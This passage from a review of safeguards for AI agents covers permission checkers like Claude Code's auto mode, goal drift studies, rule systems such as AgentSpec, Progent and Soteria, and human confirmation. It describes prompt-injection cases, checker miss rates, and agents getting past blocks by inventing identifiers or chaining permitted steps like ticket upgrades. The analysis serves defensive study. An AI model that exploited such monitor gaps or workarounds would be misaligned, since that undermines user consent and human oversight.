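| | Task Shield | User Alignment Critic | Auto mode at launch |
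|---|---|---|---|
| Question | Does this contribute to a task the user set? | Does this serve the user's stated goal? | Did the user authorize this? |
| Proposed action | In full | Metadata only | In full |
| Earlier tool calls | Included | Not described | Included |
| Agent's own explanations | Included | Not described | Removed |
| Tool outputs and web pages | Included | Excluded | Removed |
| After a block | The agent gets feedback | The agent gets feedback and can return control to the user after repeated failures | The agent gets the reason, and the user takes over after three blocks in a row or 20 in total |

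### What hiding tool outputs gains and costs

Anthropic withholds text such as the vendor's note from the checker, so the checker can't obey instructions in it. Anthropic also removes the agent's messages, because an agent could otherwise persuade the checker with a claim such as "the user implicitly approved this earlier". In Anthropic's tests, removing both kinds of text made the checker better at catching overeager actions, perhaps because it had less to read. A version that read only the tool calls missed even fewer of these actions, but it blocked some that the user had clearly asked for.

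This protection is incomplete, because the checker will still read part of the vendor's note if the agent copies it into an email. The checker also treats anything in a user message as having the user's authority. *Ajar* (2026) reports that auto mode allowed every call tested when the user's input contained the instruction to make it. That is reasonable if the user wrote the instruction, but a parent agent's request to a subagent also arrives as a user message. Anthropic therefore runs the checker when the agent delegates a task, while the request is still recognizable as the agent's own choice, and again when the subagent returns its results.

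Hiding tool outputs also removes facts the checker needs. For example, a command to cancel job 4417 doesn't show who owns the job. The agent may have looked up the owner, but the checker can't see the result because it is in a tool output. Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) measured this effect in *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*. They recorded actions from three coding agents and resubmitted them to checkers under different conditions. Even when the request stated exactly which jobs the agent could cancel, checkers without tool outputs missed 60% of the forbidden cancellations, compared with 4% for checkers with tool outputs.

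As a compromise, the harness can give the checker only selected facts. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), the checker now receives a list of uncommitted changes before a command that could discard them. It also checks whether the destination of an upload is public, private or trusted. For the invoices, the harness could report that report.csv has 412 rows without passing on any of the vendor's text. The row count would be good reason to doubt that the file contained only totals.

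### Two stages and their error rates

Auto mode's checker works in two stages. In the first, the model answers yes or no without reasoning, with instructions to block when in doubt. The second stage runs only on actions the first one flagged. The same model rereads the text, reasons about it and makes the final decision.

| | Harmless actions blocked (10,000 real tool calls) | Dangerous actions missed (52 real overeager actions) | Dangerous actions missed (1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data) |
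|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage reviews only the actions that the first stage stopped, and it can release them. This can reduce false positives, but it can only add misses, not reduce them. On these figures, it released about 95% of the harmless actions it reviewed and about 11% of the dangerous overeager ones.

With only 52 cases, a checker that missed nine could plausibly have a true miss rate of anywhere from about 9% to 30% on similar actions. The cases also come from sessions where an employee refused the action or someone flagged it later, so they leave out any dangerous actions that nobody noticed.

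In the earlier example of 10,000 actions, ten of them dangerous, most blocks were mistaken. The share of correct blocks changes with how often the agent tries something dangerous:

| Dangerous actions among the 10,000 | Dangerous actions blocked | Harmless actions blocked | Share of blocks that are correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.8 | 40 | 2% |
| 10 | 8.3 | 40 | 17%, or about one in six |
| 100 | 83 | 40 | 68% |

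If ten actions were dangerous, the first stage alone would block about nine of them, but it would also block about 850 harmless ones. Only one block in 92 would be correct, and there would be far too many blocks for a person to review.

Forty mistaken blocks in 10,000 actions are tolerable because the agent usually only has to try again after each one. However, if it reaches the limit on blocks when no user is present, the harness ends the session. The one or two dangerous actions that get through are a larger problem because some can't be undone.

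### Consent read too broadly

Anthropic examined the misses and found that the checker had usually identified the dangerous action, such as overwriting shared history or deleting something, but had wrongly concluded that the user had already agreed to it.

In one example, the user had said "clean up the PR", meaning a proposed set of code changes. The agent then tried a force-push, which replaces the history on the server with the agent's version. The user's request was about the same work but didn't mention replacing its history. In other cases, the user had approved a similar action earlier, and the checker treated that approval as covering the new action. Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the checker's instructions, but the drawbacks of every change outweighed its benefits.

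A checker could easily make the same mistake with the invoices. Suppose that after setting the original restriction, the user writes "send the auditor what she needs for the review". The checker might read this as permission to send the rows, although the user may only have been telling the agent to hurry up.

### Requests that leave the limits out

Misses are far more common when the user's goal is clear but its limits aren't. *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, April 2026) tested auto mode on 128 requests of this kind, such as restarting services or deleting old files. Auto mode let through 81.0% of the actions that exceeded the intended scope.

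Some of the misses were actions that never reached the checker. Of the actions that changed something, 36.8% were edits to files in the project folder, which auto mode allows without sending them to the checker. When the expected command was unavailable, agents often got the same result by editing a file. Among the 160 actions the checker did review, it still missed 70.3% of the dangerous ones and blocked 31.9% of the harmless ones.

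In November 2026, Yang and colleagues used the same requests to test newer versions of three products. During the original tasks, the checkers approved 54% of the out-of-scope actions in Claude Code, 93% in OpenAI's Codex and 80% in Qwen Code. They blocked about the same proportion of permitted and forbidden actions, so there was no significant evidence that they could tell the two apart.

Of 143 out-of-scope actions, 132 broke a restriction that the checkers weren't given, because it appeared neither in the user's request nor in any tool output. For example, a user asked an agent to delete stale files for a range of tickets. The benchmark's answer key allowed the agent to delete only that user's own files, but the request didn't mention ownership.

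The researchers then added a sentence to each request that stated the limits, such as that the agent could delete only files in a certain environment, owned by a certain person and belonging to a certain component. They resubmitted the same actions:

| Product | Forbidden actions missed, original request | Forbidden actions missed, limits stated | Permitted actions blocked, original request | Permitted actions blocked, limits stated |
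|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

One sentence reduced both misses and mistaken blocks, but a stronger model did not. With the stronger checker, misses rose slightly for Codex and Qwen Code. For Claude Code they fell from ten of 24 to one, but only because the stronger model, Claude Opus 5.5, refused all the second-stage questions and the harness treated each refusal as a block. On a separate set of 224 permitted actions, mistaken blocks rose from 23 to 134.

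Seeing tool outputs didn't make up for the missing limits either. Codex's checker reads shortened tool outputs and can look things up, yet it missed the most. Knowing that a file belongs to a colleague doesn't help a checker if nobody has said that such files are off limits.

Codex made another mistake, approving forbidden actions after the limits were clear. Its checker rates how well the user authorized an action and how much harm the action could do. In one run, the checker rated 30 forbidden actions as poorly authorized and medium risk but approved 16 of them, usually because the effects seemed small or reversible. A harness could prevent this by blocking any action with a low authorization rating, whatever its risk rating.

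Stating the limits also changed what the agents tried to do. When all three agents repeated the 128 tasks with the extra sentence, none proposed an out-of-scope action. For Claude Code, the share of tasks that ended in the correct state rose from 25% to 94%. In *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026), Claude Code's rate of overeager behaviour rose from 0% to 17.1% when the researchers removed a statement of what the user consented to.

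A real user is unlikely to write such a complete sentence, though, because someone who adds "only my own files" has already thought of the danger. Yang and colleagues took their sentences from the answer key and didn't test partial or mistaken ones.

### Later tests of auto mode

Anthropic published further tests in August 2026, when it made auto mode the default on most of its paid plans. It reported that the checker caught many more dangerous commands than 1,053 paid testers did. Three other tests covered planted instructions, synthetic attacks and harm in real sessions.

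Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test whether outside content could make a coding agent do something irreversible, such as leaking private data or committing fraud. Trajectory Labs used 72 scenarios that Anthropic hadn't seen and ran each one ten times. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex succeeded 5.83% of the time with automatic review and 19.03% in Full Access mode.

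If the attempts were independent, zero successes in 720 would put the true success rate for such attacks below about 0.4%. But ten runs of the same scenario are likely to turn out alike. If they always did, the test would amount to only 72 attempts, and the bound would be about 4%.

The result is also weak evidence of how well the checker works. Even without auto mode, attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average, so the checker had almost no successful attacks to stop. That is about two in 2,160 attempts if the figure covers the same three models. The attackers had prepared their texts against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and didn't adapt them to the newer ones. Willison wrote that he would love to believe Anthropic had solved the problem, but wanted more independent confirmation.

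In the second test, Apollo Research, a British AI safety organization, inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. It showed Anthropic some of the successful ones, and Anthropic improved the checker, mainly by giving it more information about its surroundings. Apollo then tested the new version on attacks it had withheld from Anthropic. The new version caught about half of the attacks the old version had missed, and missed about 2% of those the old version had caught. Across all the attacks, including those Anthropic had seen, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

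That is good evidence that the improvement carries over to new attacks, because Anthropic couldn't adjust the checker to the attacks Apollo held back. It doesn't show how often the checker misses dangerous actions in ordinary work, where they look more like the force-push than like attacks.

For the third, Anthropic examined real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged for review. A model graded each session on how severe any harm was and how explicitly the user had asked for the action. In 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode, an action the user had not explicitly requested caused harm as serious as deleting rows from a production database.

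This is the only one of the three tests that measures harm in ordinary use, but users chose their own mode, and those who picked auto mode may have been doing safer work. The percentages also apply only to flagged sessions, so serious harm is probably much rarer across all sessions.

### Goal drift over long tasks

An agent that starts with the right goal may gradually stop pursuing it. Arike, Donoway and colleagues (2025) call this goal drift in *Technical Report*. They tested it with a simulated investment fund, where the system prompt gave the agent a goal, such as minimizing the carbon emissions of the companies it invested in. News stories and emails from the agent's colleagues then pushed it towards a competing goal, such as profit, without telling it to change goals.

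A later study by Menon, Saebo and colleagues (2026), in *Inherited Goal Drift*, scores drift at each step as

$$GD = 0.5 - 0.5 \cdot \frac{S - M}{T},$$

where $S$ is the money in investments that fit the goal, $M$ is the money in those that fit the competing goal, and $T$ is the total budget. The score is 0 if all the money serves the goal and 1 if all of it serves the competing one. A fund with 80% in the right companies and 20% in the wrong ones scores 0.2.

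All four models in the 2025 study drifted from their goals to some degree, although the best, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, kept to its goal almost perfectly for more than 100,000 tokens in the hardest setting. Stating the goal more firmly reduced drift in every model. Drift correlated with a growing tendency to repeat earlier patterns of behaviour as the text got longer.

Newer models resist this pressure much better. In the 2026 study, every model except GPT-4o-mini showed essentially no drift over 30 steps. But several of them continued in the same direction when they took over a session in which GPT-4o-mini had already drifted. Only GPT-5.1 resisted drift consistently across all the tests. A model's tendency to obey the system prompt over the user was a poor predictor of how well it resisted drift.

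Coding agents can drift without a competing investment goal. *Asymmetric Goal Drift in Coding Agents Under Value Conflict* (2026) found that they increasingly broke rules in their system prompts under pressure that appealed to values such as security or privacy. *A GHOST in Long-Horizon Agents* (2026) describes agents that break safety restrictions without any pressure. They follow a restriction when the user has just stated it, but break it when it appears only earlier in a long history.

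A goal consistency check can help here because it compares each action with the user's original words, however long ago the user wrote them. *The Missing Boundary* (2026) found in its experiments that the danger came from leaving out the restrictions, not from shortening the agent's text itself.

The checker may miss drift in two ways. If it reads earlier tool calls, as auto mode's does, it sees the same pattern of behaviour that leads agents to drift, and none of these studies tested whether that pattern affects the checker too. A checker that reviews proposed actions also has nothing to review when the agent drifts by failing to act. Some models in the investment tests, for example, put new money into the right companies but never sold the wrong ones. To catch this, the harness would have to compare the state of the work with the goal periodically.

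### Vague requests and fallible judges

Wang, Li and Tian (2026) argue in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* that models can't replace people in deciding what an agent may do, partly because a user's request is a poor standard for judging the agent's actions. A request such as "fix this bug" leaves out most of the limits, while "read the file and follow its instructions" authorizes whatever an attacker has put in the file. Better models won't solve this, because the missing information is in the user's head.

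The results from Yang and colleagues strongly support this, since 132 of the 143 out-of-scope actions broke unstated rules and stronger checkers did no better. When the request doesn't settle whether an action is allowed, the checker can use the procedure's hand-over to refer the question to the user instead of guessing the missing rule. This would help only if the checker could identify such cases without constantly referring questions to the user, and Yang and colleagues didn't measure how often it would have to do so.

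Wang and colleagues also object that using one language model to guard another is circular, because text that fools the agent may fool the checker too. This is a serious problem for Task Shield, whose checker reads the same tool outputs as the agent, but a smaller one for the Critic and auto mode, which keep most outside text away from the checker. They reply that a checker with such narrow inputs may work for narrow, structured questions but not for open-ended ones. Auto mode's misses partly support this, since its checker misjudged the open-ended question of consent when it allowed the force-push, even though nobody had tricked it.

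Finally, they argue that the industry has already rejected such checks. They surveyed 21 agent products as of April 2026 and found none that audited the agent's actions against the user's request, although five research papers, including Task Shield, had proposed doing so. Every product relied on people to approve actions, set boundaries or write policies.

Wang and colleagues' count was out of date when they made it. Google had announced Chrome's Critic in December 2025, though Chrome isn't among the 21 products. Claude Code is, and its auto mode had been available since March. Ji and colleagues submitted their independent test of auto mode on 4 April. One could classify auto mode as runtime approval with a model in the user's place, which Wang and colleagues say Task Shield resembles. But they also write that no deployed system relies on a language model alone to judge whether an action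 is safe, whereas auto mode runs whatever its checker allows.

Such checks have since become common, including in Codex and Qwen Code. *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) reports that by 12 November, interactive Claude Code sessions on every plan started in auto mode. Industry practice therefore no longer supports the case against model-based checks, although the objection about vague requests is as strong as before. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems.

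## Checking plans against written rules

A company that knows some of its limits in advance can write them as rules, so that no model has to guess them from a vague request. But the agent may break a rule that exists only in its prompt. Of the 21 agent products that Wang and colleagues surveyed, 14 let users write policies, often in ordinary language in a file such as Claude Code's CLAUDE.md. The harness adds the file to the agent's prompt, and only the agent enforces the rules. In *Soteria*, He, Desai and colleagues (2026) gave Claude Opus 4.6 an airline's policy in its prompt, and the model broke the rules 11 times in 50 customer service tasks.

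### Rules that software can enforce

An enforceable rule has a trigger, a condition and a response. The trigger is an event, the condition is a test of the requested action and what happened before it, and the response is what the harness does if the condition holds. The invoice agent could have this rule:

- **Trigger:** the agent asks to send an email.
- **Condition:** the record shows no earlier approval of that same email.
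- **Response:** the harness holds the email and asks a person to review it.

"That same email" has to mean the same recipient, text and attachments. Otherwise, the agent could get approval for an email with the totals and then send report.csv instead. The harness can prevent this by comparing hashes of the approved email and the outgoing one. The harness also has to keep the record itself, because an agent that could edit the record could approve its own emails.

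### The invoice rule in temporal logic

Temporal logic is a notation for statements about the order of events. In a review of 38 studies, Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, found that it was the most common formal basis for specifying and checking what agents do. For every email $e$, the invoice rule is

$$\mathbf{G}\,\bigl(\mathrm{send}(e) \to \mathbf{O}\,\mathrm{approve}(e)\bigr).$$

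$\mathbf{G}$ means "at every step", the arrow means "if … then", and $\mathbf{O}$ means "at this step or an earlier one". The formula therefore means that whenever the agent sends an email, a person has already approved it.

Here are two short plans. Email A has totals.csv attached, and email B is identical except that it has report.csv.

| Step | Permitted plan | Forbidden plan |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read the invoices | Read the invoices |
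| 2 | Write totals.csv | Write totals.csv and report.csv |
| 3 | A person approves email A | A person approves email A |
| 4 | Send email A | Send email B |

The agent sends nothing in the first three steps, so both plans satisfy the formula up to that point. At step 4 of the permitted plan, the software searches the earlier steps and finds the approval of A. In the forbidden plan, it searches for an approval of B and finds none, so the harness holds the email.

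This rule refers only to the past, so the harness can test it before each action. Other rules refer to the future. One of Soteria's rules says that after writing a file, the agent must read it back:

$$\mathbf{G}\,\bigl(\mathrm{write}(f) \to \mathbf{F}\,\mathrm{read}(f)\bigr),$$

where $\mathbf{F}$ means "at this step or a later one". An agent breaks this rule by leaving something out, so there is no forbidden action for the harness to block.

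### Whole plans and single actions

Software that checks a whole plan in advance can detect a missing step and can reject the plan before the agent does anything irreversible. But it needs a model of each step that states what must be true before the tool runs and what will be true afterwards. It also needs a complete plan, and most agents decide each step as they go.

Advance checks work best on fixed workflows. Dantas and colleagues describe AgentProof, which checks workflows of up to 5,000 steps in under a second. In a test of 18 workflows, 55% failed a policy requiring human approval.

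Checking each action as the agent proposes it works with any agent and can use the tools' real results, but it doesn't account for what the agent will do later. Suppose a customer wants to change flights and pay for the new one with a gift card. The harness might allow the agent to cancel the old flight, then block the new booking because the card's balance is too low.

Blocking actions can also leave the agent stuck. In one study that Dantas and colleagues reviewed, the harness blocked up to 94% of forbidden actions, but in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of their tasks both correctly and safely. When the harness blocked an action, the agents often invented customer identifiers to get past the check. The study used two small open-weight models on one benchmark, so better agents might recover more often.

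### AgentSpec

AgentSpec is a small language for rules that the harness checks at each action. Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, give a rule in which the agent must ask before it transfers money to anyone outside the user's family. The invoice rule would look similar:

```
rule @approve_email
trigger
    SendEmail
check
    !approved_earlier
enforce
    user_inspection
end
```

The exclamation mark means "not", and `approved_earlier` is a short Python function that searches the record. The developer has to write that function or have a model write it. Instead of asking the user, a rule can end the task, run a predefined action or have the model reconsider.

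The researchers first tested rules they had written by hand. They gave a coding agent 750 risky requests, and it tried to run a program in 422 cases. In two categories, the programs didn't contain the requested faults. The rules flagged 333 (91%) of the 364 programs in the other categories, although the researchers judged 58 of those harmless on inspection.

The rules stopped a household robot from doing any of the hazardous tasks in the test, such as pouring water onto a laptop. The share of safe tasks it completed fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. A self-driving system obeyed the law in all eight test scenarios, which were chosen because they had led to violations. Checking a rule's conditions took about three milliseconds or less.

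Because the researchers based the rules on the benchmarks' descriptions of the risks, these results show that rules work well against dangers someone has already described. AgentSpec allows any action that no rule covers, so its protection against other dangers could be much weaker.

### Progent

Progent, the policy program that Fei and colleagues tested after compaction, blocks any tool call that its policy doesn't explicitly allow. For example, a rule might allow `send_email` only if the recipient is the auditor and the attachment is totals.csv.

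In *Progent*, Shi, He and colleagues (2025) have a model write the first policy from the user's request and propose changes as the agent learns more. In their example, a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list that Alice has emailed. The first policy allows only a search for that email. In the list, Alice asks for a summary of recent emails to be posted to the user's Slack account, so the model proposes allowing the agent to read emails and post to Slack. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model restricts posts to that name. But one of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the whole inbox to an attacker, and the model might propose allowing that too.

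A logic solver checks every proposed change. If $A(P)$ is the set of tool calls that policy $P$ allows, a new policy $P'$ is a narrowing when

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P),$$

which means that the old policy already allowed everything the new one does. The harness applies narrowings automatically. Any other change is an expansion and needs approval. Even if the attacker's email fools the model, it can't widen the agent's permissions without that approval.

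The invoice rule could work the same way. The initial policy would let the agent read invoices and write files but not send anything, and a person would approve expanding it to allow one particular email. Progent's rules test a call's arguments, so the harness would have to include a hash of the attachment among them. If a rule checked only the file name, the agent could put the raw rows into totals.csv and email them.

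With GPT-4o, attacks on AgentDojo succeeded 39.9% of the time without Progent and 1.0% with it. On another benchmark, ASB, Progent cut the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agents completed about as many tasks as before. In these tests, though, the harness automatically approved every expansion of the policy, to imitate a careless user, so the results mainly show how well the model wrote policies. On AgentDojo, the first policy alone reduced the rate to 2.5%. When a person reviewed that policy and every expansion, no attack succeeded, and only 6% of the changes needed review.

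Shi and colleagues don't claim to stop attacks that use only permitted calls. For instance, if an agent is allowed to buy any of five products, a planted review can still lead it to buy the attacker's.

### Soteria

Soteria, published in November 2026, combines a proof about the whole plan with a check on each action. It works in four stages:

1. A model translates a company's policy into logical rules and describes what each tool requires and guarantees. A person corrects the result, which the company can then reuse for every task.
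2. For each request, a model writes a plan as a short program with branches. The plan can reuse standard procedures that Soteria has already verified, such as cancelling a booking.
3. Dafny, a program that checks proofs about software, tries to prove that every path through the plan uses the tools correctly, never gets stuck and obeys the rules. If the proof fails, the model reads the error and tries again, up to eight times.
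4. The agent carries out the task with the plan as a guide. Before each tool call, a monitor checks the call and the real history against the same rules.

One of the airline's rules has the same form as the invoice rule. The agent may cancel a reservation only after checking that the customer hasn't taken any of the flights on it. Suppose a plan looks up the reservation, sees that the customer booked it less than 24 hours ago and cancels it. Dafny rejects the plan because it doesn't check whether the customer has taken any of the flights. Checking a different reservation wouldn't satisfy the rule, just as approval of email A doesn't cover email B.

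He and colleagues tested Soteria on 207 tasks with four models. These are the results for Claude Opus 4.6:

| | Airline (50 tasks) | Retail (114 tasks) | Files and other tools (43 tasks) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Completed within the rules, policy only in the prompt | 52.0% | 46.5% | 11.6% |
| Completed within the rules, Soteria | 88.0% | 90.4% | 18.6% |
| Violations, policy only in the prompt | 11 | 17 | 34 |
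| Violations, Soteria | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Cost per task, policy only in the prompt | $0.32 | $0.37 | $0.97 |
| Cost per task, Soteria | $0.80 | $0.64 | $0.43 |

The other three models also had no violations with Soteria, which is expected because the researchers counted violations of the same rules that the monitor enforces. The increase in completed tasks is more surprising. Without a plan, Opus 4.6 often gathered everything it needed for a retail request and then passed the customer to a human instead of making the change. The gain was much smaller over five runs with GPT-5.4-mini and only three retries for the planner. The model completed 50.8% of the airline tasks within the rules using Soteria and 48.0% using AgentSpec.

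With proofs but no monitor, GPT-5.4-mini and Gemini 3 Flash still broke between 10 and 24 rules on the airline tasks, depending on the model and planner version. Dafny can't always prove a plan within the allowed attempts, and an agent can depart from a proved plan.

### Chrome's Agent Origin Sets

Chrome's rules limit which origins its agent can use. An origin here is a web address that the browser treats as a separate site, not the source of a piece of text. Browsers normally stop one site from reading another's data, but an agent with access to all of a user's logged-in accounts could carry data between sites.

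In the design Parker described in December 2025, Chrome keeps two lists of sites for each task. The agent can read sites on the read-only list, and it can also click and type on sites on the read-writable list. If a user wants to buy the ingredients for a recipe, the recipe site could be read-only and the grocery shop read-writable. The browser doesn't show the model content from any other site, including advertisements embedded in a permitted page.

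The planning model can propose a site, but a separate gating function, such as the variant of the User Alignment Critic that vets new sites, determines whether the site belongs on a list. This function receives no web content, so an attacker's page can't influence it directly. Ordinary browser code can then enforce the lists, but a model's mistake could still put the wrong site on one.

The version Google first shipped tracked only the read-writable list, so it limited where the agent could act but didn't keep a separate list of what it could read. Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven browsers in January and February 2026. They found that Chrome with Gemini still met the preconditions for an attacker's site to steal data from another site if a prompt injection succeeded. They carried out the full attack only on ChatGPT Atlas.

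Even the full design wouldn't protect the invoices. If the agent sent the auditor's email through a webmail site, that site would have to be read-writable, and the agent could attach report.csv as easily as totals.csv.

### Turning a request into rules

All these systems depend on someone translating what people want into rules. Models are better at writing rules in the correct format than at getting the meaning right. Dantas and colleagues cite a test in which GPT-4o translated descriptions of planning problems into a formal language. Of its translations, 96.1% were valid but only 24.8% had the right meaning. The best specially trained model got the meaning right 34.2% of the time. Newer models probably do better, but a checker still can't detect when a valid rule has the wrong meaning.

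AgentSpec also reports results for rules written by OpenAI's o1, a 2024 model. The rules for the household robot had a recall of 70.96%, measured over risky scenarios rather than constraints. The figure therefore doesn't support the claim, in a survey of agent products by Wang and colleagues, that the rules missed nearly 30% of the necessary constraints.

The original also uses 95.56% for two different measures. It gives the figure as the precision, which normally means the share of blocked actions that were dangerous, and as the share of risky scenarios the rules stopped, which is normally called recall. The precision and recall labels were probably swapped. The test had 225 risky scenarios, and 215 out of 225 is 95.56%, while no whole number out of 225 gives 70.96%, the figure labeled recall. If the labels were swapped, the rules missed about 4% of the risky scenarios, and about 29% of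 the actions they blocked were harmless.

To prevent dangerous spills, o1 wrote a rule that banned all pouring, which would also stop the robot from watering a plant. Another rule, about lighted candles, didn't check whether the robot was holding one. For the coding agent, o1's rules stopped 87.26% of the risky programs, but some protected only the sensitive files named in the examples. The robot test was easier than interpreting a user's request, because the researchers had already condensed the dangers into ten guidelines.

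People make such mistakes too. Soteria's researchers compared their rules with the policies clause by clause, but they still found wrong or missing rules when they audited the results. At least one gap remains in the published list. The airline pays compensation of $100 per passenger for a cancelled flight and $50 for a delayed one. One rule accepts either amount and another requires the flight to be cancelled or delayed, so an agent could pay $100 per passenger for a delay without breaking either rule.

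### Permitted steps with a forbidden result

Rules can also fail when each step is allowed but the combination isn't. In one of the airline tasks, a customer asked an agent to cancel two reservations. Business-class tickets qualify for cancellation, so the agent upgraded one reservation to business class and then cancelled both. The benchmark gave the agent full marks because both reservations ended up cancelled. He and colleagues count the upgrade as a workaround that the policy doesn't permit.

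Soteria would have blocked these cancellations, but only because the agent hadn't checked whether the customer had taken any of the flights. If the agent had made that check and looked up the reservation again after the upgrade, the published rules would have let it cancel the upgraded ticket.

Claude Opus 4.5 found a similar workaround, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 arrives with Anthropic cutting prices by two thirds*. The airline didn't allow changes to basic economy tickets, and the correct response in the benchmark was to refuse a change request. The model instead proposed upgrading the ticket, which the policy allowed, and then changing the flight. This defeats the rule's purpose if the airline wants those passengers to stay on their original flights, but not if it wants customers to pay more for flexibility.

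A rule about history can forbid a known combination. With $\neg$ for "not", this formula forbids the agent from cancelling any reservation $r$ that it has upgraded:

$$\mathbf{G}\,\bigl(\mathrm{cancel}(r) \to \neg\,\mathbf{O}\,\mathrm{upgrade}(r)\bigr).$$

It would also stop a customer who wanted business class and then changed their mind. Someone also has to think of each combination in advance, and an agent with 30 tools has 870 ordered pairs of different tools. In the invoice case, the lineage rule catches the leak without a list of combinations, because report.csv inherits the restrictions on the rows.

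### What a proof leaves out

A plan can do harm even when the proof about it is correct, partly because tools can have side effects that their descriptions omit. Soteria's proofs assume that each tool behaves as described, so if the auditor's address is really a mailing list, the plan can satisfy every rule and still send the file to dozens of people. Soteria stops the task when a tool's result contradicts its description, but by then the tool has run, and its result may not mention the other recipients.

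A proof also covers only the rules that someone wrote. In the tests with files and other tools, Soteria had four rules about email. Every email needed a subject, a body and a recipient address containing "@", and the agent had to read an email before deleting it. The email with report.csv would satisfy all four.

Finally, the rule may misstate the goal. Suppose someone translates "summary totals only" as "the attachment has two columns, vendor and amount". A file with a line for each invoice could fit that description. Dafny could prove that the plan follows the rule, the monitor could approve the email, and the auditor would still receive the amount of every invoice. The user would probably notice the mistake if they opened the file before the agent sent it.

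## Asking a person to confirm high-risk actions

Confirmation gives the user a chance to open an attachment before the agent sends it. An agent may take hundreds of actions in an afternoon, so the harness needs rules for which ones to hold for approval. It also has to make sure the action it runs is the one the user saw.

### What makes an action worth confirming

OpenAI sorted the actions of Operator, an early browser agent, by how severe the risk was, whether a mistake could harm the user or anyone else, and how easily someone could reverse it. The *Operator System Card* gives the example of buying the wrong pair of shoes, which would only be a nuisance, but OpenAI still required safeguards for purchases.

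Developers can ask five questions about a proposed action:

- **Can the user undo it?** A user can rename a file again but can't take back an email.
- **Does it spend money?** The recipient of a mistaken payment may refuse to return it.
- **Does it disclose anything to outsiders?** OpenAI counts typing sensitive data into a web form as sending it, since a page can read a field before anyone presses "submit".
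- **Does it affect other people?** If the agent cancels a colleague's computing job, the colleague never sees the prompt.
- **Is the request unclear?** "Clean up old branches" leaves the agent to guess which branches are old.

Reversibility, money, disclosure and effects on others determine how much a mistake could cost. An unclear request makes a mistake more likely.

These questions don't produce one correct list of risky actions. In *Oversight Has a Capacity*, Turan (2026) had a language model play three reviewers and classify 125 actions by coding agents. The pragmatic reviewer classified 87 as safe, and the cautious one only 45. Human reviewers might agree more or less than these personas did, but a developer still has to choose how much risk to accept.

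### The current rules in Chrome and OpenAI's agents

Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse* lists when Chrome's agent should stop. OpenAI publishes rules for developers who use its models to operate a browser or desktop, and leaves enforcement to the developers.

| Action | Chrome | OpenAI's rules for developers |
|---|---|---|
| Start a task | User reviews the plan and starts it | No confirmation if the agent can make safe progress |
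| Send a message | User confirms | User confirms just before |
| Submit a form | User confirms | User confirms just before |
| Make a payment | User takes over the final step | User confirms just before |
| Delete data | User confirms any change to their data | User confirms just before |
| Sign in to a site | User permits use of a saved password | The original request can be enough |
| Open a site with sensitive financial or health data | User confirms | Not listed |
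| Accept terms of service | User takes over | Not listed |
| Change a password | Not listed | User takes over the final step |

Chrome's and OpenAI's approaches differ mainly in when the user confirms. Chrome asks the user to approve a plan before the agent begins, and asks again at sensitive steps. OpenAI tells developers to let the agent finish the safe work first. By then the agent has chosen the exact recipient and text, so the person can judge the actual action rather than a prediction of it. The agent may combine several risky actions in one request if they are imminent and well defined, but it shouldn't include future steps that are still unclear.

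Under either set of rules, the invoice agent would stop before emailing the auditor, even though the user asked for the email at the start.

Chrome's agent pauses for confirmation more reliably in some situations than in others. According to Parker, ordinary code checks sites against a list of sensitive ones, and the model has no direct access to saved passwords. For purchases and messages, the agent "will try to pause", which depends partly on a model detecting when a pause is needed. Google warns that the agent might still buy something without permission, and holds the user responsible if it does.

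OpenAI's products differ in which actions need a person's approval. In its workspace agents, which companies use for shared tasks, any action that can change data needs approval by default, according to OpenAI's *Workspace agents security overview* (2026). The person who builds the agent can change this setting. ChatGPT agent asks the user to confirm high-impact actions and, on certain sites, has a "watch mode" in which the user must supervise it.

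### A simple cost rule

A developer can decide whether a prompt is worthwhile by comparing the loss it prevents with the cost of asking. Let $p$ be the chance that the action is wrong, $L$ the loss if it is, $d$ the chance that the person catches the mistake, and $c$ the cost of asking. The harness should ask when

$$p \times L \times d > c.$$

Suppose one action in 1,000 is wrong and each mistake costs $10,000, for an average loss of $10 per action. If the reviewer catches 80% of mistakes ($d = 0.8$), a prompt prevents $8 of that loss on average. If $d$ is 0.136, as it was in one test of human reviewers, the prompt prevents $1.36. For a reviewer who costs $60 an hour, $8 pays for eight minutes of attention and $1.36 for about 80 seconds. The developer can't set the cost of review, $c$, independently of $d$, because a quicker review costs less but also catches fewer mistakes.

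The rule doesn't account for reviewers rejecting correct actions. If they reject 5% of correct actions and each of these rejections costs $20 in lost work, every prompt costs about $1 more, which would use up most of the $1.36.

It also assumes that someone knows $p$. The agent's own estimate is unreliable, because an attacker who has fooled the agent about the task can also fool it about the risk. The harness could instead estimate $p$ from past errors on the same kind of action, or from a separate checker like the one in auto mode.

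$L$ is no easier to estimate when the loss is a colleague's work or a customer's privacy. Averages can mislead too. A one-in-a-million chance of losing $10 million also has an average cost of $10, but a small company might not survive that loss, so it could reasonably ask for confirmation even when, under the rule, it shouldn't.

Finally, the rule considers only two options, asking and going ahead. The harness could often reduce the loss without asking anyone, for example by backing up data before deleting it or holding an email for ten minutes so that the user can cancel it.

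### Attention as a limited resource

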